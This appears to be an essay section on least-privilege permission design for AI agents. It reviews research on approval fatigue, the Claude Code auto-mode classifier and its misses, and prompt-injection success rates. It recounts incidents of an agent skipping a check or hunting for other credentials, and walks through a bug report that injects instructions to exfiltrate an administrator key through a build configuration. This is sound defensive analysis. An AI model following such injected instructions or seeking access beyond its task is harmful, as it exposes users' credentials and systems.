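Both experiments used simulated, interchangeable tools, whereas real tasks often require several tools together. Newer models such as GPT-5.6 Sol and Claude Opus 5 may also behave differently. Similar training has continued in *Task-Conditioned Least-Privilege Learning for Executable Terminal and MCP Agents*, for which Tu and Tu (2026) trained a small model partly on these scenarios. Parkinson and colleagues report that a least-privilege instruction helped that model more after training than before.

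### What users approve

If an agent chooses too powerful a tool, a person asked to approve the action could still stop it. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, published on 25 March 2026, reports that users approved 93% of a coding agent's prompts. By August, Anthropic gave the figure as 97%. The company does not say whether both figures cover the same kinds of users and prompts, so the increase may not mean that people became less careful.

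A high approval rate does not prove that people approve requests without reading them, because if 97% of the requests were harmless, a perfect reviewer would approve 97% of them. Anthropic's comparison with other decisions is more suggestive, since users rejected 39% of the plans Claude presented before starting work.

An experiment that planted dangerous commands gives better evidence. Anthropic had a research company recruit 1,053 paid testers, who knew they were in a coding study but not which behaviour it measured. One approval request in each session showed a clearly dangerous command, though approving it ran nothing harmful. Only 143 testers (13.6%) rejected it. The rejection rate was about 17% when the command appeared early in a session and about 5% when it followed 50 or more other requests.

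The testers worked in a special environment and had no projects of their own to lose, so real users might be more careful. Even so, the decline during a session suggests that frequent requests make approval less useful.

Anthropic's alternative is auto mode, in which a separate classifier based on a language model reviews actions that could do damage. It blocked 89% of the dangerous commands shown to the testers. In the March tests, it wrongly blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary actions and missed 17% of 52 real actions in which Claude went beyond what its user wanted. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier identified the danger but wrongly treated the action as approved by the user. For example, it treated a request to clean up a proposed code change as permission to overwrite the project's history.

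Auto mode also ignores saved rules that approve any shell command or any Python script, because the classifier would otherwise never see those commands. Since 14 August 2026 it has been the default for new Claude Code sessions on Anthropic's Pro, Max and Team plans, unless the user or an administrator chose another setting. On 22 October Anthropic announced that auto mode would become the default in most Claude apps on those plans the following week. The 93% figure therefore applies to a way of working that is no longer the default for many users.

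Many people had already stopped reviewing every command. Anthropic reports that a quarter of interactive sessions started with permission checks turned off altogether.

### When an agent does harm

Some of the real incidents that Anthropic describes resemble the experiments on tool choice. In three of them, Claude met an obstacle and sought access that its user had not offered. In the first, a check failed before Claude could install a new version of some software, and Claude tried again with an option that skipped the check. In the second, Claude could not upload a report to an internal drive and tried to publish it on a public code-sharing site. In the third, Claude received a login error and began searching files for other credentials.

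An agent can also go too far because its instructions are vague. *Coding Agents Are Guessing* (2026) tested five combinations of agent and model on tasks that left out important details. In 55.8% to 67.8% of runs, the agent crossed at least one limit on what it was supposed to do, whether or not this caused damage. Signs of how much damage an action could cause barely reduced the agents' tendency to act.

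Anthropic tried to measure serious harm more directly by examining Claude Code sessions from May and June 2026. It found severe harmful actions that the user had not explicitly requested, such as deleting data from a working database, in 6.3% of sessions where users approved actions themselves and 2.4% of sessions in auto mode.

Anthropic looked only at sessions that its safety systems had already flagged, from users who had agreed to share their data, so these rates don't describe ordinary use. A language model judged the severity. Users also chose their own mode, and those who chose manual approval may have been doing riskier work. The comparison is therefore weaker evidence than the experiment with dangerous commands.

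Agents with similar permissions can also differ greatly in how often attacks on them succeed. Trajectory Labs, a company that Anthropic hired, tested 72 prompt injection attacks ten times each on several models. Against GPT-5.6 Sol with full access, 19.03% of the attempts succeeded. Against Anthropic's latest models with permission checks turned off, the average was 0.09%. The company had developed the attacks against an older Claude model and did not test some of the protections in either developer's own browser software, so the results do not measure the risk of using either product.

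## Designing permission sets for AI agents

Experience with Linux capabilities suggests seven rules for deciding what an agent may do. Most of the links drawn here between capabilities and agent permissions are inferences. Researchers who work on agents usually cite the general principle of least privilege, and Christodorescu and colleagues compare agents' permissions with those of Android apps and with SELinux.

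### An agent with four permissions

Suppose Alice works for a small company and has an agent that handles bug reports about the company's website. The agent may read her mail, send mail from her address, edit the website's code repository and change its build configuration, a list of commands that a build server runs whenever the code changes. The build server holds a token for writing to the repository and a key for logging in as administrator to the company's main machine, which runs the website and the mail.

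| Permission | What Alice wants it for | What it can lead to |
|---|---|---|
| Read mail | Finding bug reports | Control of any account that sends password-reset links to her mailbox |
| Send mail | Answering customers | Disclosure of anything the agent can read, and requests to colleagues in Alice's name |
| Edit the repository | Fixing bugs | Changes to the public website, and commands on the build server if it runs tests stored in the repository |
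| Change the build configuration | Updating the build tools | Any command on the build server, with its token and key |

The last permission effectively grants the other three. An attacker who controls the agent can add a command that uses the token to edit the repository and the key to log in to the main machine. From there the attacker can read and send everyone's mail, including Alice's. If the build server did not hold that key, the attacker could still edit the repository and send data out, but could not open Alice's mailbox this way. As with CAP_IPC_OWNER, judging the permission requires knowing what else is on the system.

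Taking this permission away would not be enough. If the build server runs tests from the repository, an attacker can put the same command in a test, so permission to edit the repository is almost as powerful.

The two mail permissions are also dangerous together. Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa adopt a rule that an agent should never combine untrusted input, sensitive data and a way to send data out or change things. Reading Alice's inbox gives the agent the first two, and permission to send mail gives it the third.

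### Defining the permissions

Spengler found routes to root from 19 of the 35 capabilities Linux then had, so a permission should be judged by everything it can lead to. Luo, Shen and colleagues (2026), in *PRISM*, partly automate this for agents. They draw a graph with an arrow from one tool to another if the first tool's output fits an input that the second requires, or if text from the first tool's output turned up in the second tool's input in earlier runs. An attacker who controls the result of one tool may be able to follow the arrows to others. The researchers calculate a "blast radius" for each possible starting point and try to keep the worst one small:

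```
blast radius = high-risk tools the attacker can reach / all high-risk tools
```

Without this calculation, the agents completed almost as many tasks (77.8% instead of 78.2%), but the blast radius rose from 15.9% to 27.3%. Two permission sets can therefore be about equally useful but differ greatly in what an attacker gains. Studies that only count the capabilities removed from a program don't measure this difference.

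Such a graph is never complete. In 200 tests it included 93.8% of the reachable tools. The seven cases it missed all involved credentials that the agent had passed on in ordinary language. The graph also covers only the agent's tools. It would show that Alice's agent can change the build configuration, but it wouldn't show the administrator's key, which somebody would still have to know about.

The name CAP_SYS_ADMIN describes a role, so kernel developers could fit any privileged operation under it. An agent's permission should instead be named after an operation, such as "change the build configuration". Amazon's cloud service partly does this by classifying every action as listing, reading, tagging, writing or managing permissions. GitHub's repository roles, which run from Read to Admin, are closer to the Linux mistake of naming a permission after a role.

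However, administrators have good reasons to want roles. Microsoft's *least privilege for ai agents identity access and tool binding* (2026) warns against running agents without managed identities and role-based access. Luo and colleagues argue that a separate set for every task would be hard to review or reuse. A role does little harm if it is only a list of named operations and the service checks for each operation rather than for the role. An administrator can then read the list and remove operations from it. CAP_SYS_ADMIN cannot be narrowed this way because the kernel checks for the whole capability, not the individual operation.

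The catch-all also grew because nobody coordinated where new operations went. Agent tools multiply much faster than privileged operations in the kernel. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* cites a count of 177,436 tools created between November 2024 and February 2026. Someone should therefore be responsible for deciding which permission covers each new tool.

In *Capability Minimization as a Safety Primitive*, Iyer and Babu (2026) rate a tool's risk as low if it only reads, medium if its changes are easy to reverse, and high if its changes are irreversible or visible to outsiders, or if it transfers money. Two people rated each tool in the test set, and when they disagreed, the tool got the higher rating.

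One company cannot inspect every tool that outsiders write, and cautious reviewers might rate so many tools as high-risk that the category becomes another catch-all. It would do less harm than CAP_SYS_ADMIN, because a high rating in Iyer and Babu's scheme only requires confirmation before the agent can use that one tool. But it would also lead to more confirmation requests, and people seem to check requests less carefully when they see many.

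### Limiting permissions and passing them on

Linux cannot restrict CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE to particular files. An agent's permissions should limit which objects it can act on, as well as which actions it can take. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) does this with rules about the arguments of a tool call. For example, a rule might let an agent send messages to only one recipient. Progent blocks any call that no rule allows.

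These rules work only if they cover every argument that identifies an object. *The Same Zero* (2026) describes a check that looked for recipients in fields called `recipient`, `to`, `account`, `target` and `email`. It did not cover the fields `recipients`, `cc` and `bcc`, which are used by the mail tool in AgentDojo, a widely used collection of simulated tasks and attacks. Limiting a message's content is harder, because a rule that allows mail to a customer does not restrict what the agent may tell her.

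Morgan objected to the ambient set because a service could pass a capability to programs that nobody had prepared to receive it. For the same reason, an agent that hands part of its work to a sub-agent should have to state which permissions the sub-agent gets. In the system described in *Authority Is Not a String*, the agent's request names the sub-agent's role, its subtask and the permissions it should have. The sub-agent can receive only permissions within a limit set for the whole task.

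Permission sets do not control how agents influence each other. Suppose a sub-agent can only read mail, but it reports to an agent that can change the build configuration. A malicious message might reach the more powerful agent through the report, without any transfer of permissions. *A Theory of Least Autonomy in AI* (Parisel, 2026) therefore counts an agent's own permissions together with those of the agents it can influence, if the possible damage exceeds a threshold that the organisation chooses. The method deliberately overestimates the danger, since an agent may not obey a malicious message it receives.

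Sendmail became dangerous because it kept running after failing to drop root privileges. A missing permission should instead cause a failure that the agent and its user can see. When Progent blocks a call, it returns the reason to the agent, with a prompt to try other tools or arguments.

An agent that an attacker has manipulated can use the explanation for a refusal to look for another way to do the same thing. Agents in the experiments on tool choice also tended to choose more powerful tools after errors, although those errors were temporary faults rather than refusals. Explanations are therefore safe only if the rules also block the alternatives.

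Iyer and Babu avoid refusals by hiding a risky tool until the conditions for using it are met. For example, an agent sees the tool for sending mail only after the recipient is confirmed. The agent cannot call the tool too early, but it may also be unable to tell its user which condition is missing. The protection fails completely if text from a message can mark the recipient as confirmed, and it does not catch harmful arguments once the tool is available.

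Finally, the set has to be small enough to administer, which Schaufler thought impossible with the 330 capabilities of DG/UX. PRISM groups similar tasks into roles and stops adding roles when another one would hardly improve the results. It produced 6.7 roles on average, compared with 13.1 with a simpler grouping method. Each role still allowed about ten tools, so an agent will often have access to tools that its current task does not need.

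A calculation cannot always identify one best permission set. *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026) shows that two sets can both be minimal although neither contains the other. Someone then has to decide which is worse to grant. PRISM leaves some of these decisions to people by offering several sets for each role. In one example, an administrator could choose between letting an agent create a bug report and letting it comment on an existing one.

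### Redesigning the set

Alice could replace her agent's four permissions with these rules:

```
allow read_mail     if the message is the bug report for this task
allow create_draft  if to contains only the report's sender
                    and cc and bcc are empty
allow edit_file     if the repository is "website"
                    and the branch starts with "agent/"
                    and the file is not part of the build configuration
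block everything else
```

The agent now writes drafts, and Alice sends them. It edits a branch, which is a separate copy of the code, and a colleague reviews the changes before they reach the website. The agent has to ask a person to make any changes to the build configuration.

The company must also change the build server, which the agent's rules do not cover. Tests for the agent's branches should run on a separate machine with no token, key or network connection. Otherwise the agent could still put commands in a test, and the build server would run them with the company's credentials.

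Suppose an attacker sends a bug report with hidden instructions to upload the administrator's key. Under the old permissions, the agent could add the upload command to the build configuration, and the build server would run it. Under the new ones, Progent or a similar system blocks that edit. If the agent puts the command in a test instead, the test finds no key and cannot send anything out.

The attacker sent the report, so the attacker is the only person to whom the agent may address a draft. If the agent could read all of Alice's mail, it might put other customers' messages in the draft, and Alice would have to notice them before sending it. The first rule therefore allows only one report at a time. The draft could still disclose private code from the repository, and a reviewer could overlook a harmful change to an ordinary file.

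The company also loses some convenience. The agent can no longer answer a customer without Alice or repair a broken build configuration by itself.

### How research systems narrow permissions

Nobody could write permission rules by hand for every request. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (2026) reports that the agent frameworks it examined let developers limit which tools an agent has, but do not check by default whether each call is authorised.

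Progent uses a language model to write the rules. Suppose a user asks an agent to carry out the tasks in a colleague's email. The initial rules allow only a search for that email. In it, the colleague asks for a summary of recent mail to be posted on Slack, a messaging service, so the model proposes allowing the agent to read mail, look up the user's Slack account and post there. Once the agent has found the account name, the model restricts posting to that account.

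Progent treats these two changes differently. It compares the set of tool calls that the old rules allow with the set that the new rules allow:

```
new calls are all among the old calls:  apply the change
otherwise:                              ask for approval
```

A solver, a program that reasons about logical formulas, compares the new rules with the old ones. If another email tricks the model into proposing a rule that lets the agent forward the inbox to a stranger, the solver detects that the new rules allow more, and Progent asks for approval before applying them.

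On AgentDojo, Progent reduced the attack success rate from 39.9% to 1.0% with GPT-4o and kept the agent about as useful. On ASB, another collection of attacks, it reduced the rate from 70.3% to 3.9%. Most of the attacks that still worked on ASB used tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of the tools the task needed.

In these tests, Progent automatically approved every request for wider permissions to imitate a careless user. The low attack rates therefore reflect how well the model wrote rules, not how much the approval step helps. When a person reviewed the initial rules and every expansion, no attacks succeeded. Only 6% of changes needed approval, which would give a real user fewer requests to review, but ordinary users may review them less carefully.

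*MiniScope* (Zhu, Tseng and colleagues, 2025) uses permissions that services already define for OAuth. The agent submits a plan, and MiniScope calculates the smallest set of permissions that covers the tools in it. MiniScope then prompts the user to grant any that are missing, checks every call against the set and keeps the user's credentials away from the agent. When language models chose the permissions instead, commercial models found the smallest set in 70–83% of cases and open-source models in 20–34%.

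In a simulation of three months of Gmail use, MiniScope asked for confirmation in 18% to 60% of cases, depending on the type of user. It does not stop an attack that stays within a permission. If the user has allowed the agent to send mail, for example, MiniScope does not check whether the recipient makes sense.

PRISM tests which tools a task needs by removing some in a simulated environment and checking whether the agent can still finish. From 512 runs on each collection of tasks, it learns to predict which other sets of tools would be sufficient. In one task, an agent had to find a failed software release in the logs and report it. Without the tool for reading cloud files, its success rate fell from 93% to 5%. Removing the command shell made no clear difference, although agents had used it in 31% of runs. Granting every tool that agents had used would have included the shell, much as tracing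 the kernel's checks can add capabilities that a program does not need.

Before a new task, PRISM selects a role based on the task's description. If the choice is uncertain, it grants only the tools that the two most likely roles share and prompts the user about the rest. This happened in 6.8% of sessions.

Parkinson and colleagues describe AgenTRIM as limiting the tools an agent sees at each step. Sharma, Jiang and colleagues propose a narrower approach, PAuth, which aims to authorise only the particular operation in a request.

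Several groups have compared such defences. *Bounded Agents* (2026) tested Progent with handwritten rules, as did Luo and colleagues. *The Same Zero* tested a simpler defence in which a language model picks the tools for a task and removes the others.

| Defence | Tested by | Successful attacks | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Progent, rules written by a model | Shi and colleagues | 1.0% (39.9% without it) | About as many as without it |
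| Progent, handwritten rules | *Bounded Agents* | 0% | 59.7% in banking and 88.5% in office work, during attacks |
| Progent, handwritten rules for each type of task | Luo and colleagues | 20.5% (58.2% without it) | 76.3% (79.4% without it) |
| PRISM | Luo and colleagues | 6.1% (58.2% without it) | 78.2% (79.4% without it) |
| Removing whole tools | *The Same Zero* | 0.0% | 25.0% |

The rows are not directly comparable. Luo and colleagues counted an attack as successful if the agent carried out any high-risk action, while under AgentDojo's own measure, an attack succeeds only if it achieves the attacker's goal. They also used different models and wrote Progent's rules themselves. Their figures for completed tasks cover two other task collections as well as AgentDojo. The result for removing whole tools comes only from banking tasks with one DeepSeek model.

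Even so, the last row shows why a low attack rate is not enough: an agent that cannot use its tools is hard to attack but of little use. Shi and colleagues explain that allowing or removing whole tools either takes away a tool the task needs or leaves it available for any purpose. Rules about arguments can keep the mail tool available and block only the wrong recipients.

Progent's results also depend heavily on who writes the rules and how researchers count attacks. Newer systems may do better. *PACE* (2026) reports fewer successful attacks and more completed tasks than Progent on AgentDojo with all three models it tested.

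### When the task decides what an agent needs

Christodorescu and colleagues object that an agent, unlike `ping`, has no fixed program that an administrator can analyse once to work out what permissions it needs. Linux has a milder form of this problem with `rm` and Python, which are poorly suited to file capabilities. This is a good reason not to attach one permanent set of permissions to an agent. The rules for defining permissions still apply, because permission to change the build configuration leads to the same dangers whatever Alice asks her agent to do.

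Many requests also contain enough information to derive a useful permission set. When Shi and colleagues had Progent generate rules from the user's request and kept those rules fixed, the attack success rate on AgentDojo fell from 39.9% to 2.5%. The method works less well for a request such as "do what this email asks", because nobody can know which permissions the agent needs until it has read the email.

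Requests that leave more to the agent are also easier to attack, so limits matter most in the tasks where permissions are hardest to predict. *AutoDojo* (2026) divided banking tasks into three groups by how much they left to the agent. Without any defence, attacks on Gemini 2.5 Flash succeeded in 66.7% of the most open tasks, 23.2% of the middle group and 13.9% of the fully specified ones.

A permission set derived from a request can also be too broad because someone has manipulated the request. Progent assumes that whatever the user writes is harmless, but Zhu and colleagues do not, because users may paste in text from a web page or a customer's message. Suppose Alice's request includes a pasted bug report in which someone has written that the repair requires access to the build configuration. Progent's model might include that access in the initial rules. The solver would not detect the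 mistake, because it only compares later rules with earlier ones, so someone would have to review the initial rules.

MiniScope has a related weakness. It calculates the smallest set of permissions for the agent's plan, so if an attacker has influenced the plan, the set may be the smallest one that allows the attack. The user can refuse a permission, but she has to recognise that her task does not need it. The system in *Authority Is Not a String* reduces this risk by setting the limit for a task before the agent reads any repository text or tool output. Text the user pasted into the request could still affect the limit.

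No message can change a fixed permission set, but a set that has to cover everything an agent might do for Alice will be too broad for most tasks. Checks on arguments can narrow each action if someone knows the acceptable values in advance. In *The Same Zero*, a check allowed transfers only to the six accounts that already existed in the simulated bank. This would block a transfer to an attacker's new account, but also the first payment to a new landlord.

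The three methods work better together. An owner can set a fixed outer limit, a model can derive a smaller set for each task, and argument checks can examine each call. A manipulated request can then widen the set only as far as the outer limit, much as the bounding set limits what a program file can grant in Linux. Noyan's *Dynamic Capability Scoping for Enterprise AI Agents* proposes a similar design with a fixed limit for each role, a classifier that examines the task, and a list of forbidden combinations.

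Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa's version, called elastic least privilege, also limits how long an agent keeps a permission. The agent always has a small baseline of permissions and can borrow others up to a limit set by its owner. In their example, it can borrow permission to read for up to 60 minutes and permission to write for up to 20. Borrowing uses up a budget that refills over time, and sub-agents share their parent's budget. Leaving aside a surcharge for repeated requests, the cost is:

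```
cost per minute = sum of weights / (1 − p)
```

The weight is 1 for reading, 3 for writing and 9 for administration. `p` is the share of a forbidden combination that the session already contains. Suppose an agent has read public bug reports, which are untrusted input, one of the three elements of the forbidden combination. Reading the code then uses 1 / (1 − 1/3) = 1.5 units per minute. Permission to write to a public repository adds a second element, so reading and writing together use (1 + 3) / (1 − 2/3) = 12 units per minute. Adding the third element would make the rate infinite, so the system refuses the request.

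The agent can see these costs and return a permission early. In the example, an agent that reads the code first and holds write permission only during the repair spends 93 units, including the surcharge. Requesting both read and write permission for 20 minutes at the start would have cost 240.

The researchers also simulated an attack in which a malicious bug report makes the agent borrow access to one private repository after another. The agent gets access to eight before the budget stops it, and it could have copied them all by then, so the budget limits the damage but does not prevent it. The rule against forbidden combinations stops the agent from publishing the copies, because a session that has read private data cannot write to a public repository, even after its read permission expires.

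These numbers illustrate a proposal that nobody has yet tested as a whole. The rule that stops the attack would also hinder ordinary work. If Alice's agent read her inbox, it could not send mail in the same session unless she approved an exception. Starting a new session would not help, because the agent would have to read the message again to answer it.
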